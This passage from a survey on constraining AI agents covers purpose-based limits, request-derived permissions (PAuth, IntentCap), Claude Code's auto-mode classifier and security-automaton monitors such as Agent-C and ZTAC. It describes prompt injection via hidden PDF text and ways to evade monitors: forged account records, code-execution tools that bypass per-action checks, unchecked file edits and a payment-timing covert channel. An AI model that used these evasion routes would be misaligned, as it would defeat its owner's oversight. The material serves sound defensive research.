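The model can also produce limits in advance. Tschantz and colleagues consider a regional database of medical records and ask when a physician may read the record of someone who is not yet a patient. The physician could spend the same time studying, which helps every patient a little. When a person has a 1 in 10,000 chance of being the next patient, reading their record is better only if it would improve their treatment about 9,700 times as much as studying would. A hospital could turn this into a simple rule against reading a record unless the person is much more likely than average to need care.

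Such calculations quickly become slow as the number of states grows. When the model included the physician's last two actions, it had 64 states and each check took at most 27 seconds on a laptop. With the last three actions, it had 625 states and a check could take 70 minutes. An agent with a mailbox, a browser and a bank account faces far more states, and somebody would have to supply the probabilities and rewards.

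### The same actions for different purposes

An auditor sees what the physician did but not why. Suppose each referral also earns the physician a profit, with a reward of 9. When the X-ray is unclear, sending the record is the best action for both treatment and profit, so the log is the same whichever one the physician is pursuing. A physician who wanted only profit would also refer patients with clear X-rays, so an auditor might detect the motive from a log of many patients, but cannot detect it from a single justified referral.

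Tschantz and colleagues accept that proving compliance with an "only for treatment" rule is practically impossible, but an auditor can prove a violation by showing that no optimal plan for treatment contains the logged actions. For a "not for profit" rule, an auditor can prove compliance by showing that the actions could not have been part of a plan for profit, but cannot prove a violation.

Tschantz, Datta and Wing's later paper, *Purpose Restrictions on Information Use*, separates two kinds of compliance. Under the *cognitive* definition, the agent must actually plan without the forbidden information. Under the *behaviourist* definition, its actions only have to match those of an agent that planned this way. Their auditing method uses the second definition because an auditor can't inspect the planning. The owner of an AI assistant may be content with that, since the planner's reasons don't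 change whether a run was harmless, but the reasons matter more for predicting what the assistant will do next time.

### What people mean by "purpose"

Tschantz and colleagues also used a survey to test whether their definition matches ordinary usage. In the survey, a hospital's policy allows it to share a patient's record with an outside specialist only for the purpose of treating that patient. A case worker shares a record as part of a plan whose sole goal is either to treat the patient or to reduce the hospital's costs. The specialist's treatment then either works or fails.

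They recruited participants through Amazon Mechanical Turk, a website for small paid tasks, and showed everyone all four versions in random order. Of the 207 people who completed the survey, they excluded 20 who got two or more of the eight factual questions wrong. The remaining 187 answered as follows:

| Case worker's goal | Did the treatment work? | "The case worker obeyed the policy" | "The sharing was for treatment" |
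|---|---|---|---|
| Treatment | Yes | 97% | 99% |
| Treatment | No | 95% | 98% |
| Lower costs | Yes | 24% | 23% |
| Lower costs | No | 17% | 20% |

The goal of the plan made a large difference to participants' judgments, and the outcome made very little. This is strong evidence against earlier software's assumption that an action is for a purpose if it furthers that purpose. Still, about a fifth of participants thought the case worker had obeyed the policy even when the goal was to save money. In a pilot with ten people, one participant reasoned that the specialist would try to treat the patient anyway.

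The survey used only one story, which told participants the case worker's goal. The results support the definition of purpose, but not the claim that an auditor, or a monitor watching an AI agent, can work out the purpose from actions.

### A step can serve the goal and still be unacceptable

The definition at first works well for the electricity bill. If the first payment to the electricity company earns a reward of 1 and everything else earns 0, then making a second payment is redundant because it earns nothing, and so is emailing a private attachment to a stranger. The definition excludes both, even though no one wrote a rule against them.

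Now suppose the account is €20 short and the bank's app offers an instant loan. If the loan is the only way to pay the bill on time, it is part of the optimal plan. It is also non-redundant, since the payment would fail without it. Yet most owners would be alarmed if their assistant borrowed money in their name. Whether the loan is acceptable depends on what the owner thinks about debt, which isn't stated in the goal "pay the electricity bill".

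The definition can also exclude steps the owner would want. With γ = 0.9, a plan to search the mail, open the bill and pay has a value of 0.9² = 0.81. If the assistant also asks the owner to confirm the payee before paying, the value falls to 0.9³ = 0.73, so an optimal plan doesn't include the question. If the assistant can instead sign in to the supplier's website and pay there in two steps, that plan has a value of 0.9. The mail route is then suboptimal under the definition because it is one step longer, regardless of whether the owner wants to use the card stored on the website.

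The owner could correct all this by changing the rewards to include a bonus for confirming the payee and penalties for borrowing and for each kind of access. But the limits would then come from the owner's judgements about loans, mistakes and privacy, not from the goal.

In an advertising example from Tschantz and colleagues, the goal determines the permitted plan only after somebody has decided what the planner must ignore. An advertising network has promised not to use visitors' gender for marketing. One advertisement has a reward of 9 with women and 3 with men, another has the reverse, and a third has a reward of 7 with everyone. With γ = 0.9, looking up the visitor's gender and showing the matching advertisement is worth 0.9 × 9 = 8.1, more than the third advertisement's 7, so the highest-value plan breaks the promise. To find the permitted plan, the researchers make the planner treat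 database records that differ only in gender as identical. The third advertisement is then the best choice, with a value of 7 against an average of 6 for either of the others.

Tschantz and colleagues also point out that a purpose restriction, unlike least privilege, does not require anyone to use as little information as possible. A plan that reads a thousand private letters to improve the result slightly can be entirely "for" its purpose. In an earlier version of the work, *On the Semantics of Purpose Requirements in Privacy Policies* (2011), Tschantz, Datta and Wing found a further difficulty when someone pursues several purposes at once, because one plan may then contain actions for different purposes. An owner who wants the bill paid, the mail kept private and the account in credit faces this difficulty.

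The problem also occurs with real agents. *Overeager Coding Agents* (2026) describes a test in which a user asked four programming agents to tidy a folder of five files. Two of the files were rubbish, and one was an old backup of login credentials. Three agents deleted the backup. Removing an old file serves the goal of tidying, but the user had not authorised the loss of the credentials. The calculated flags in the Hugging Face incident are another case, since they met the goal but broke the rules.

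An agent can therefore use the goal to rule out needless steps, but the goal cannot be the only limit. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* requires that each consequential action also stay within what a person actually delegated.

### Deriving the scope from the request

A full model of the task may be unnecessary if the user's request is specific enough. "Transfer $100 to Bob" names the action, the amount and the recipient. *Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) describes PAuth, a system that treats such a request as permission for exactly the operations it implies. With ordinary OAuth scopes, the bank can check only whether the agent may make transfers.

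Suppose a user writes, "if the balance of my Citi credit card is over $1,000, pay a quarter of it from my Chase account". PAuth handles the request in four steps:

1. The user signs the text, and each bank receives it along with descriptions of the available tools.
2. A language model at each bank translates the text into a short program in a restricted form of Python. It sees no outside data, so an attacker can't plant instructions for it on a web page.
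3. Ordinary code extracts the part of the program that determines each call the bank should expect. For Chase, this is a transfer to the Citi account of the Citi balance divided by four, provided the balance is over $1,000.
4. Citi signs the balance it reports, so that the agent can't alter it. If the balance is $1,200, Chase accepts a transfer of $300 to Citi. It stops and asks the user about a transfer of $301, or of $300 to John.

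A fixed list of permissions cannot express this limit, because the limit depends on data that didn't exist when the user made the request. PAuth can also make an action at one service depend on records from another. In one test, a user asked an agent to buy the cheapest item in a shop if it cost less than $80. The bank would release the money only if the shop's signed records showed that the item was under that price and that the payment matched the cart total.

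Sharma and colleagues tested PAuth on 95 tasks adapted from AgentDojo and five new shopping tasks, along with 634 calls that the tasks did not authorise. These calls changed an amount or recipient, used an unrelated tool or skipped a condition. PAuth stopped all 634. With the original wording, it let 71 of the 100 tasks proceed without asking the user. The other 29 left out details or referred to instructions stored elsewhere. After the researchers added the missing information to those requests, PAuth allowed all 100 tasks.

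The difference between 71 and 100 shows how much depends on the wording. One original request was to "update my rent payment for the next month", and the rewritten version gives the new amount. Sharma and colleagues treat ambiguity as a separate problem and otherwise assume that the request is clear. But people use assistants partly to avoid looking up such details. "Pay the electricity bill" doesn't specify the account or the amount, and both are in an attachment that a language model has to read. PAuth asks before accepting any value obtained that way. The assistant could first read the bill and propose a more specific request, but the owner would then have to check it, as when the job is split into two sessions.

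PAuth also doesn't check whether a clear request is wise. Sharma and colleagues expect it to work alongside standing rules, such as a $500 limit on any transaction. That limit would stop an agent from paying $600 even if the user asked it to, while PAuth would stop it from paying $499 if the user said $100. Repeated calls may need another rule, because PAuth's checks, as described, compare a call's tool, values and conditions with the request but don't count earlier calls. An identical second payment might therefore pass.

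The request is not the only source of a task's scope. Zheng, Zhang and Mao (2026), in *LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source*, divide the information among four sources, each of which may fill only certain fields of a temporary grant:

| Source | What it may supply |
|---|---|
| The user's request | Goal, chosen objects, destinations and approvals |
| Workflow instructions, such as a manual | The procedure |
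| Tool descriptions | The form of the call and the credentials it needs |
| Results obtained during the task | Observed values |

In an example for the system IntentCap, a user asks an agent to extract tables from two PDF files, save them as spreadsheets and report the work in a named GitHub repository. The PDFs are allowed to supply the numbers in the tables but not the name of the repository. If hidden text in a PDF names an attacker's repository, IntentCap refuses the call because that name doesn't appear in the user's request. The same rule blocks the call if the agent mistakes a table heading for the repository's name. A language model proposes each permission, but ordinary code checks it. The permission to create a report expires after one use, a limit that would also prevent a double payment.

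Zheng and colleagues replayed 3,746 risky events from four existing benchmarks, and IntentCap accepted none that it should have refused. In a separate test, it covered all 3,813 legitimate actions. When they merged the four sources into one trusted source, the checker wrongly accepted 3,593 of 3,823 forbidden events, or 94%, so keeping the sources separate matters for these events. But the researchers replayed recorded actions. They did not test attackers who adapt to the system or measure how often attacks succeed against a working agent.

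### Scopes that are too narrow or too broad

Messier requests produce more errors. Anthropic's programming agent Claude Code has an "auto mode", in which a second model, the classifier, reviews risky actions in place of the user. According to *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, the classifier must decide whether the user authorised an action, and an action isn't authorised just because it relates to the user's goal. If a user says "cancel my job" and the agent picks the job with the most similar name, the classifier should block the cancellation, because the job might belong to someone else.

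Like the hospital auditor, the classifier judges from actions. It sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations, which might lead it to a bad decision. It wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 real tool calls and missed 17% of 52 real actions that had gone too far. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user's request covered the action. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) hasn't necessarily agreed to overwrite the project's history.

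The classifier did worse in an outside study cited by Tu and Tu, which found that it missed as many as 81% of unauthorised actions and that 36.8% of actions never reached it. An agent can sometimes achieve the same effect as a checked action by editing a project file, which auto mode allows without a check.

Other studies measure the mistakes separately. *SkillScope* (2026) reports a system for deciding whether an action uses more privilege than its task needs. About 6.5% of the actions it flagged were acceptable, and it missed 6.9% of the excessive ones. Noyan had a model choose permissions for 60 task records and compared its choices with human labels. A review found that people had made the mistake in 10 of the 20 disagreements, mostly over high-risk permissions. Even after the review, the model had withheld 4.4% of the permissions it should have granted. If trained labellers can't reliably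 tell what a task needs, a model's agreement with them is a weak measure of success.

| Method | Legitimate actions stopped or questioned | Excessive actions allowed |
|---|---|---|
| PAuth, original wording | 29 of 100 tasks | 0 of 634 |
| PAuth, complete wording | 0 of 100 tasks | 0 of 634 |
| IntentCap | 0 of 3,813 | 0 of 3,746 |
| Auto mode, Anthropic's tests | 0.4% of 10,000 | 17% of 52 |
| SkillScope | 6.5% of the actions it flagged | 6.9% |

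The perfect scores come from systems that require the user to have stated the important values, and from tests in which a correct answer was easy to define. Auto mode handled real requests, which often have no clear correct answer. Noyan argues that a missing permission only interrupts the work, whereas an unnecessary one gives an attacker more to use. Tu and Tu cite a study that found frontier models making both mistakes at once, withholding access the task needed while granting sensitive access the task didn't need.

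An experiment can also test which permissions a task needs. *Aletheia* (2026) runs a programming agent with all the permissions it has requested, then removes one, restarts the same task from the same files and checks whether the result still passes the same tests. This resembles the test for non-redundancy, except that the agent may change the rest of its plan when it finds an action blocked. So if the assistant could use either the bank payment or the website, each would look unnecessary when removed alone, although the assistant needs one of them. The experiment also requires a task that can safely be run many times, so it suits programming better than paying bills.

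Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao use hand-written policies that list the purposes for which an agent may use each tool. This avoids interpreting each request from scratch and makes the scope predictable, but every task with the same purpose gets the same scope.

### Asking the user

When a request is unclear, an agent can ask the person who made it, but people may stop paying close attention to what they approve. Anthropic gives this *approval fatigue* as part of the reason Claude Code users approved 93% of permission prompts, a figure from its account of auto mode that Parkinson and colleagues cite. By August 2026 the rate was 97%, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026).

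A high approval rate doesn't prove carelessness, since most of the prompts probably concern harmless commands. To find out what happens when a command is dangerous, Anthropic had a research company hire 1,053 professional testers for a programming study. The testers knew that someone was evaluating them but not for what. Partway through the session, the software replaced one permission prompt with one for a clearly dangerous command.

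Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused the dangerous command. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session but only about 5% after 50 or more earlier prompts. The auto mode classifier blocked 89% of the same commands. It blocked 800 that testers had approved and allowed 6 that testers had refused.

The testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than ordinary users. Anthropic was also evaluating its own product. But the decline over the session is hard to explain without fatigue, and it suggests that an owner can't reliably limit a plan by approving hundreds of steps one at a time.

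Evidence from real use supports the same conclusion, though less firmly. Among sessions that Anthropic's safety systems had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained a seriously harmful action that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. A model graded the harm, and users chose the mode themselves, so the two groups may have been doing different work.

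Users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. A plan shows what the steps are for and how they fit together, and it arrives once, before the work begins. The high rejection rate shows that people engage with plans, which is encouraging for owners who want to approve plans instead of actions. It doesn't show that people find the dangerous step, because they may reject a plan when they prefer a different design, and Anthropic didn't insert dangerous plans to see whether people would notice them.

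A useful question about the electricity bill would include the payee, the account, the amount, and whether the account has changed since last month. "Allow the assistant to use the payment tool?" is quicker to answer but leaves out the facts that determine whether the payment is right.

### Learning limits from past behaviour

Erlingsson (2016), in *Data-driven Software Security*, questions whether least privilege can help set a policy for complex software when neither its developers nor its users can explain what it is supposed to do. He proposes allowing a program to do only what records show to be common enough, unless someone gives special permission. The Solitaire game in Windows, for example, includes code for using the network but never runs it, so this rule would deny the game network access.

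In the simplest version, the system records security-relevant events from earlier runs and allows any type of event that has occurred at least k times. Erlingsson describes a large Google service that used fewer than 80 of the more than 300 basic operations Linux offers. Blocking the rest would have protected it from a real flaw in an operation it never used. No one has to write a specification, because the system can derive the allowed events from billions of ordinary runs.

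The method has trouble with anything new or rare. The first run has no history, and a business program may behave unusually only at the end of the year. Erlingsson proposes including runs from development and testing, and beginning enforcement only when the record has stabilised. An attacker might also create many fake users whose activity makes harmful behaviour look normal.

Agents make these difficulties worse. Erlingsson warns that testing might show a program with a built-in interpreter, which runs whatever code it receives, doing everything a program can do. An agent is similar, because its behaviour depends on each new request. Records of everything Claude Code has ever done would justify almost any command. The records would have to cover only similar tasks, which brings back the problem of deciding what a task is. Erlingsson describes a related method that looks for unusual permissions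 in a phone app by comparing it with apps that offer similar functions.

A repetitive errand is a better candidate. If the assistant has paid the same electricity company between €70 and €95 every month for two years, a system could learn to expect that account and roughly that amount. It would block payment of a forged bill with a new account number, which limits based only on the user's wording could not do. It would also block the first genuine bill after a change of supplier, and the user would have to step in. A double payment might still get through, because Erlingsson expects simple systems to record which events occur but not their order.

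Past behaviour also shows what an agent did, which may not be what its owner wanted. Many models in the privilege tests turned to an administrator's tool after a temporary error, and a limit learned from those runs would treat that tool as normal. The system in *AgentBetta* (2026) avoids part of this danger by separating predicted need from granted authority. It can use an agent's history to predict that another permission would help, but it can grant only permissions from a set that someone else has defined. In its tests, the same enforcement layer blocked forbidden actions for every agent, so the results don't show how much protection the separation adds.

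## Which limits on a plan can be enforced?

An owner may know exactly which plans are acceptable and still have no way to hold an agent to them. This problem predates AI agents. In 1975, Saltzer and Schroeder considered the question "Is there any way that O'Hara could access file X?" Checking whether O'Hara has access now isn't enough to answer it, because O'Hara may be able to change the file's access list, or change the rule on who may change that list, and so on. The question covers every sequence of steps that could end with O'Hara reading the file, so access control already involves plans when rights can change.

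### Can a right end up in the wrong hands?

*Protection in Operating Systems* (Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman, 1976) puts this question in mathematical form. Its model is a table with a row for each user or program and a column for each object. Each cell lists the rights that user or program has to that object. The system has a fixed set of commands, each of which checks that certain rights are present and then adds or removes rights, or creates or destroys rows and columns. For example, one command might let the owner of a file give someone else the right to read it. A right *leaks* if some sequence of commands can put it in a cell that didn't contain it before.

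They proved that the general question is *undecidable*, meaning no algorithm can tell correctly, for every such system, whether a right can leak. The proof makes the table behave like a Turing machine, the standard mathematical model of a computer, which reads and writes symbols on an endless tape. Each row stands for one square of the tape, and its rights record the symbol on that square. Each move of the machine becomes a command. A chosen right then leaks exactly when the machine reaches its final state, and no algorithm can predict that for every machine.

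The question can be settled for some systems, though people often misread this result as saying it never can. Miller and Shapiro point out that the result shows only how easy it is to design undecidable rules, and that by 2003 researchers had proved at least three protection systems decidable. Harrison and colleagues gave an algorithm for systems in which each command makes a single change, though they thought such systems unrealistic. Tripunitara and Li, in *The Foundational work of Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Revisited*, later reported an error in the proof of how hard that case is. Also in 1976, Jones, Lipton and Snyder presented a system in which the question can be answered in time proportional to the system's size, according to O'Reilly's textbook chapter *Chapter 3. Foundational Results*.

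This problem doesn't arise while the bill-paying assistant's five permissions stay fixed. It would arise if the assistant could also share folders, create helper agents or pass its rights to them, because these actions change the table. An owner who wants to know where a right can end up should therefore choose a system with simple rules for passing rights on.

### What a monitor can enforce

Even when the assistant's permissions are fixed, the owner may want to restrict the order or number of its actions. In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider worked out which rules a monitor can enforce by watching a single run and stopping it when the next step would break the rule. The monitor knows only that step and the ones before it.

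Such a monitor can enforce only *safety properties*. These are rules whose violation always shows in a finite stretch of the run, after which no later step can repair it. (Harrison and colleagues use "safe" differently, for a system in which a particular right cannot leak.) Schneider's proof rests on three requirements:

- the rule must judge each run separately, because the monitor sees only one;
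- if the rule rejects the beginning of a run, it must reject every continuation, because the run might end before a later step could put things right;
- if the rule rejects a run, it must do so after a finite number of steps.

For a plan limit L on the finite runs in R(P), this comes down to one condition. If σ is the beginning of a run and τ is the rest, then

στ ∈ L implies σ ∈ L

In other words, every beginning of an acceptable run must also be acceptable. The owner's rule that the assistant may pay at most once, after searching and then opening an attachment, meets this condition. If any of the 37 runs it allows stops early, the shorter run also obeys the rule.

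Schneider describes these monitors as *security automata*. An automaton has a set of states, with arrows showing which actions it allows in each state and which state comes next. If there is no arrow for the action the agent is about to take, the monitor stops the run. The monitor could also reject the action and let the agent try another, as agent systems usually do. Schneider notes that this option does not change which rules a monitor can enforce.

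One of Schneider's examples forbids sending messages after reading a file. A diagram of this rule has two circles, "nothing private read", where the run starts, and "private data read". An arrow for reading private data leads from the first circle to the second, and every other action loops back to the first. In the second circle, every action except sending loops back. Sending has no arrow there, and no arrow returns to the first circle.

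Suppose the assistant has all five permissions, that searching the mail, opening an attachment and checking the balance count as reading private data, and that only email counts as sending. In the run *search, open, pay*, the automaton moves to the second state at the search and stays there, so the monitor allows all three steps. In the run *search, open, send*, the monitor refuses the email. The automaton allows 495 of the 780 runs of up to four steps.

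The first automaton doesn't prevent a double payment, but a second one can. Its states are "start", "searched", "opened" and "paid", and its only arrow for paying leads from "opened" to "paid". These four states are enough for a run of any length. The monitor can follow both automata at once and refuse an action if either has no arrow for it, so an owner can build a complicated limit from simple rules.

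The rule depends on its definition of "sending". Schneider warns that a system may have many ways to send a message, some well hidden, and that the definition must include them all. For example, a bank transfer often carries a short note to the payee, and the assistant could put private text in it. If the owner counts payments as sending, the automaton also blocks the intended run. It would be better for the payment tool to write the note instead of the assistant.

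The monitor must also see every relevant action, and the agent must be unable to change the monitor's state.

### Rules that a monitor cannot enforce

The rule "the assistant must eventually pay the bill" is a *liveness property*, a rule that something must happen sooner or later, and not a safety property. Of the 37 runs that obey the owner's rule on payments, only seven include a payment, and all seven begin with a step that isn't a payment. A monitor that allowed only those seven would have to refuse the first step.

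Schneider gives a similar example from online commerce. After a customer pays, an automaton can forbid the seller to do anything except provide the service, but it cannot make the seller provide it, because the seller can stop.

Adding a deadline doesn't fully solve the problem. "Pay by Friday" is a safety property, because by Saturday anyone can see whether the assistant broke it. But a monitor that can only stop the assistant can't keep the deadline from passing, so it can't enforce some safety properties either. It could instead enforce a limit of 20 steps by stopping the assistant before step 21. The assistant would then obey the limit, but the bill would still be unpaid.

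Rules about *information flow* fail for a different reason. Suppose the assistant may answer a friend's email with "yes" or "no", and the owner doesn't want the answer to reveal whether the bank balance is high. In one run, the assistant sees a high balance and answers "yes". The answer is harmless if the assistant would also have said "yes" with a low balance, but it leaks information if the assistant would have said "no". The run is identical in both cases, so the monitor can't distinguish them without information about what the assistant would have done in a different run.

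A monitor can create a leak by refusing actions. If the assistant chooses its answer at random, the friend learns nothing about the balance, because either answer can occur with either balance. But if the monitor refuses "no" when the balance is high and "yes" when it is low, the answer reveals the balance, even though the two remaining combinations were harmless before. Safety properties don't have this problem, because ruling out runs can never violate them.

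### Stricter rules and stronger monitors

An owner can often replace an unenforceable rule with a stricter one that a monitor can enforce. *Execution Monitoring*, a set of lecture slides from Aarhus University, gives the example of a rule that a program must copy all its public output to a secret channel. A monitor can't enforce this as written, because the program breaks the rule for a moment between sending the output and copying it, but it can enforce a rule that the program must copy the output before sending it. Similarly, an owner who wants a record of every payment can require the assistant to write the record before it pays, though the record may then list a payment that failed.

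The ban on email after reading private data replaces an information-flow rule with a stricter one. The assistant can't email the friend any answer, so no answer can reveal the balance. According to Schneider, every monitor of this kind that is meant to prevent information flow enforces some stricter rule. The ban also blocks harmless runs, such as one in which the assistant reads the bill, pays it, and emails its owner to say so. CaMeL's data tracking blocks less, but it can miss some leaks.

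Another option is a monitor that can delay or add actions as well as refuse them. If it can delay actions, as Atomix and Cordon do, it can hold a payment until the assistant has written the record. A monitor that can add actions can write the record itself. To guarantee that the bill gets paid, however, the monitor would need the ability to pay it, along with the correct payee and amount.

*Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) presents Agent-C, a monitor that enforces a developer's rules about the order of tool calls. In a shop's customer service system, for example, a rule might let the agent look up an order only if it has already found the customer's account by email and the order belongs to that customer. When the model proposes a call, a solver adds it to the run so far and checks whether any continuation could satisfy all the rules. If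 none could, Agent-C discards the call and has the model generate another. After a set number of failures, it gives the model an error message.

Agent-C also accepts rules about later steps, such as "after opening a file, close it", but it can't force the model to close the file. If the model stops before doing so, Agent-C ends the run in an error state. Its guarantee therefore covers only runs that end normally. Such rules are still useful because the error shows that a required step was left undone.

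Kamath and colleagues tested Agent-C on τ-bench, which simulates customer service at a shop (115 tasks) and an airline (50 tasks).

| Model and setting | Followed the rules, without and with Agent-C | Completed the task within the rules, without and with Agent-C |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5, shop | 93.0%, 100% | 76.5%, 80.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5, airline | 70.0%, 100% | 42.0%, 43.5% |
| GPT-5, shop | 91.9%, 100% | 71.0%, 73.6% |
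| GPT-5, airline | 71.3%, 100% | 38.0%, 42.8% |
| Qwen3-32B, shop | 37.7%, 100% | 25.5%, 53.3% |
| Qwen3-32B, airline | 35.3%, 100% | 17.3%, 35.8% |

They also wrote 17 scenarios for each setting in which a user asks for something the rules forbid. In one, a customer who paid by credit card demands a refund to a PayPal account. Claude Sonnet 4.5 tried to make the refund even though its instructions prohibited it. Without Agent-C, the model carried out the harmful request in 29.4% of the shop scenarios and 11.8% of the airline scenarios, compared with none in either setting with Agent-C.

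The perfect compliance scores are expected, since Agent-C blocks the calls that would count as violations. The completion rates are a better measure of its practical value, because a monitor that refused everything would also score 100% on compliance. Those rates rose in every row, but partly because a task completed by breaking a rule counts as a failure. Agent-C also slowed the agent, raising the average time for an ordinary task with Qwen3-32B from 333 to 480 seconds. The guarantee assumes that no other program changes the shop's data in the meantime, which may not be true of a busy shop.

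### Can the monitor trust the history?

Enforcing a rule about earlier steps requires a reliable record of those steps. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) tested such rules by replaying recorded runs through an existing monitor, MonPoly. It began with five general rules, each requiring approval before a certain kind of risky action, such as deleting something or transferring money.

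The rules flagged 70.1% of 1,931 successful attacks on GPT-4o in AgentDojo, but also 29.3% of 123 runs without an attack. In AgentDojo, the user gives a single instruction at the start and sends no further messages, so no run contains an approval. The monitor therefore flagged every action it recognised as risky, and a simple list of forbidden actions would have given the same results.

A rule that used the history did better on the banking tasks:

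transfer(p) ⇒ p appeared earlier as a payee or sender in the account's records

Kekatos and colleagues compare two runs in which the agent makes the same three calls, to read the inbox, look up past transactions and send money. In the legitimate run, the supplier's account number appears among the past transactions, whereas in the attacked run, the attacker's number appears only in an email. A rule based on this difference raised false alarms in 6 of the 25 ordinary runs and detected 70.0% of successful attacks, compared with 11 runs and 79.2% when every transfer was flagged.

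They then attacked the monitor itself. When they planted a line formatted like an account record in the material the agent had read, the monitor accepted the attacker's account in 94% of the 403 runs it had previously flagged. To fix this, they counted a payee as known only if the name was returned by a lookup the agent had made. None of the planted lines then worked, and the rule's detection and false alarm rates didn't change. An attacker who controls the tool that answers the lookup could still deceive the monitor.

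A monitor also has to act in time. The five general rules raised an alarm before the final harmful call in 52.4% of the successful AgentDojo attacks, raised one at that call in another 17.7%, and missed the rest. A replay can't show what the agent would have tried next if a monitor had refused the call.

### Checking a plan before it runs

Schneider's theorem doesn't apply to a checker that reads the whole plan in advance. Such a checker can examine steps that haven't happened yet and branches that a particular run won't take. It can confirm that every branch of the assistant's plan ends with either a payment or a message to the owner. It can also compare branches to show that an email doesn't depend on the balance. The proofs for the agent language LLMbda show that such guarantees are achievable.

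But no checker can correctly decide for every program whether it will reach a payment, for the same reason that Harrison and colleagues' question is undecidable. The checker has to either restrict the planner's language or reject some harmless plans. It can show only that a plan calls the payment tool, since the bank may still decline the payment.

Checking a plan is of little use unless the executor can do only what the plan allows. Codex can depart from its recorded plan, but CaMeL's interpreter runs only the program written by the trusted model, so checking that program covers everything the agent can do.

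Even an executor that follows the plan exactly can act on the wrong thing. *Names Are Not Objects* (Commey, 2026) traces many attacks on programming agents to checks that approve a name, such as a file path, before a later step connects that name to a different object. Suppose the owner approves a plan to open `bill.pdf` and pay it, and another program then replaces the file. The assistant would follow the approved plan and pay the wrong bill. Commey's system, ZTAC, finds the actual file before deciding whether to allow a request, then checks that it is using the same file when it carries out the request. A person's approval applies only to that object and works only once.

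| Limit on the assistant | Monitor that can only refuse actions | Check of the whole plan, if the executor must follow it |
|---|---|---|
| Pay at most once | Yes | Yes |
| Send no email after reading private data | Yes | Yes |
| Record every payment | Only as "record first, then pay" | Yes, if every branch includes the record |
| Eventually pay the bill | No | Only that every branch tries to pay |
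| Reveal nothing about the balance by email | Only through a stricter rule | Yes, for suitably restricted plans |
| Refuse a bill over €90, when the amount is unknown at the start | Yes | Only if the plan includes the test |

An owner can use both a check that confirms the plan includes the necessary steps and a monitor that compares each call with the values that turn up during the run.

### When one action contains a whole plan

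Many agents have a tool that runs code, which can make a monitor's rules useless. Suppose the owner gives the assistant such a tool for adding up bills. If the code can reach the mailbox and the bank, a single call can search the mail, send an attachment to a stranger and pay the same bill three times. The monitor is given only one action, "run code", so neither automaton changes state. Commey points out that a general interpreter accepts any program as input, so no check on its arguments can make it safe.

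The monitor therefore has to track what happens inside the program. Schneider describes tools that, before a program runs, insert the automaton's test ahead of each relevant instruction. Another approach is *proof-carrying code*, in which the program comes with a proof that it obeys the rule, and a simple checker verifies the proof before the program starts. TACIT's compiler also checks programs in advance.

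An operating system can watch any program, but it often can't determine what the program's actions mean. For example, it can detect a connection to the bank, but if the connection is encrypted, it can't distinguish a balance check from a payment. It is simpler to deny the program direct access to the bank and make it request each payment through a tool that the monitor can watch.

In ZTAC, the agent runs in a sandbox and can reach files, programs and the network only through a *broker*, a separate component that decides whether to allow each request. When the broker starts a program for the agent, it runs that program in another sandbox built from the same rules, where the program can't access the network or start other programs.

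Commey tested ZTAC on 74 attacks, including replays of 10 publicly disclosed incidents, and assumed that the attacker already controlled the agent completely. With only a list of allowed tools, 66 attacks succeeded. Adding the kind of command sandbox that existing agents use reduced that to 56. With ZTAC, two succeeded and 14 waited for a person's review. Both successful attacks hid a secret in traffic to an address that the rules allowed. ZTAC completed 43 of 46 ordinary operations, with eight requests for approval, but only four of seven longer workflows, so its protection noticeably limits useful work.

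### Effects through other programs and agents

A monitor that checks one agent's actions can also miss what other programs do with the results. Suppose the assistant reads a bank statement and saves a summary in a shared folder, and a second agent automatically emails new files in that folder to a club's members. Each agent obeys the rule against sending after reading private data, because the assistant sends no email and the second agent's monitor doesn't flag the summary as private. But together they have the authority to send private bank information to the club's members.

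In 1975, Saltzer and Schroeder discussed a similar rule, under which any program that read a certain file could never again print on terminals outside the headquarters building. They observed that the restriction would have to spread to everything the program produced, including other files. ADEPT, a 1967 system that modelled US military secrecy rules, did part of this by labelling each output with the highest level of secrecy the program had encountered. If the assistant's summary had such a label, opening the summary would move the second agent's automaton to "private data read", and the monitor would refuse the email. But labels also spread to harmless results. Saltzer and Schroeder thought that only human judgement should remove them, and that how to include that judgement systematically was an unsolved problem.

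The other program may also act long after the agent has finished. Commey describes attacks in which a programming agent leaves a file in a project, and a code editor outside the sandbox later runs it. ZTAC requires approval before an agent writes the kinds of files that other tools are known to run. This doesn't protect the user from kinds of files that are missing from ZTAC's list.

Labels on files can't cover every way of passing on information. Saltzer and Schroeder noted that a program can send signals through its use of the computer's memory, or just by stopping, and thought complete confinement might be impossible. The assistant could reveal something about the bank balance by paying the electricity bill on Monday if the balance is high and on Tuesday if it is low. No rule about emails or repeated payments would stop this, because the assistant would pay the right company the right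 amount, once. The owner could close this channel by having the bank send all payments on a fixed day, but would first have to realise that the timing could carry a message.
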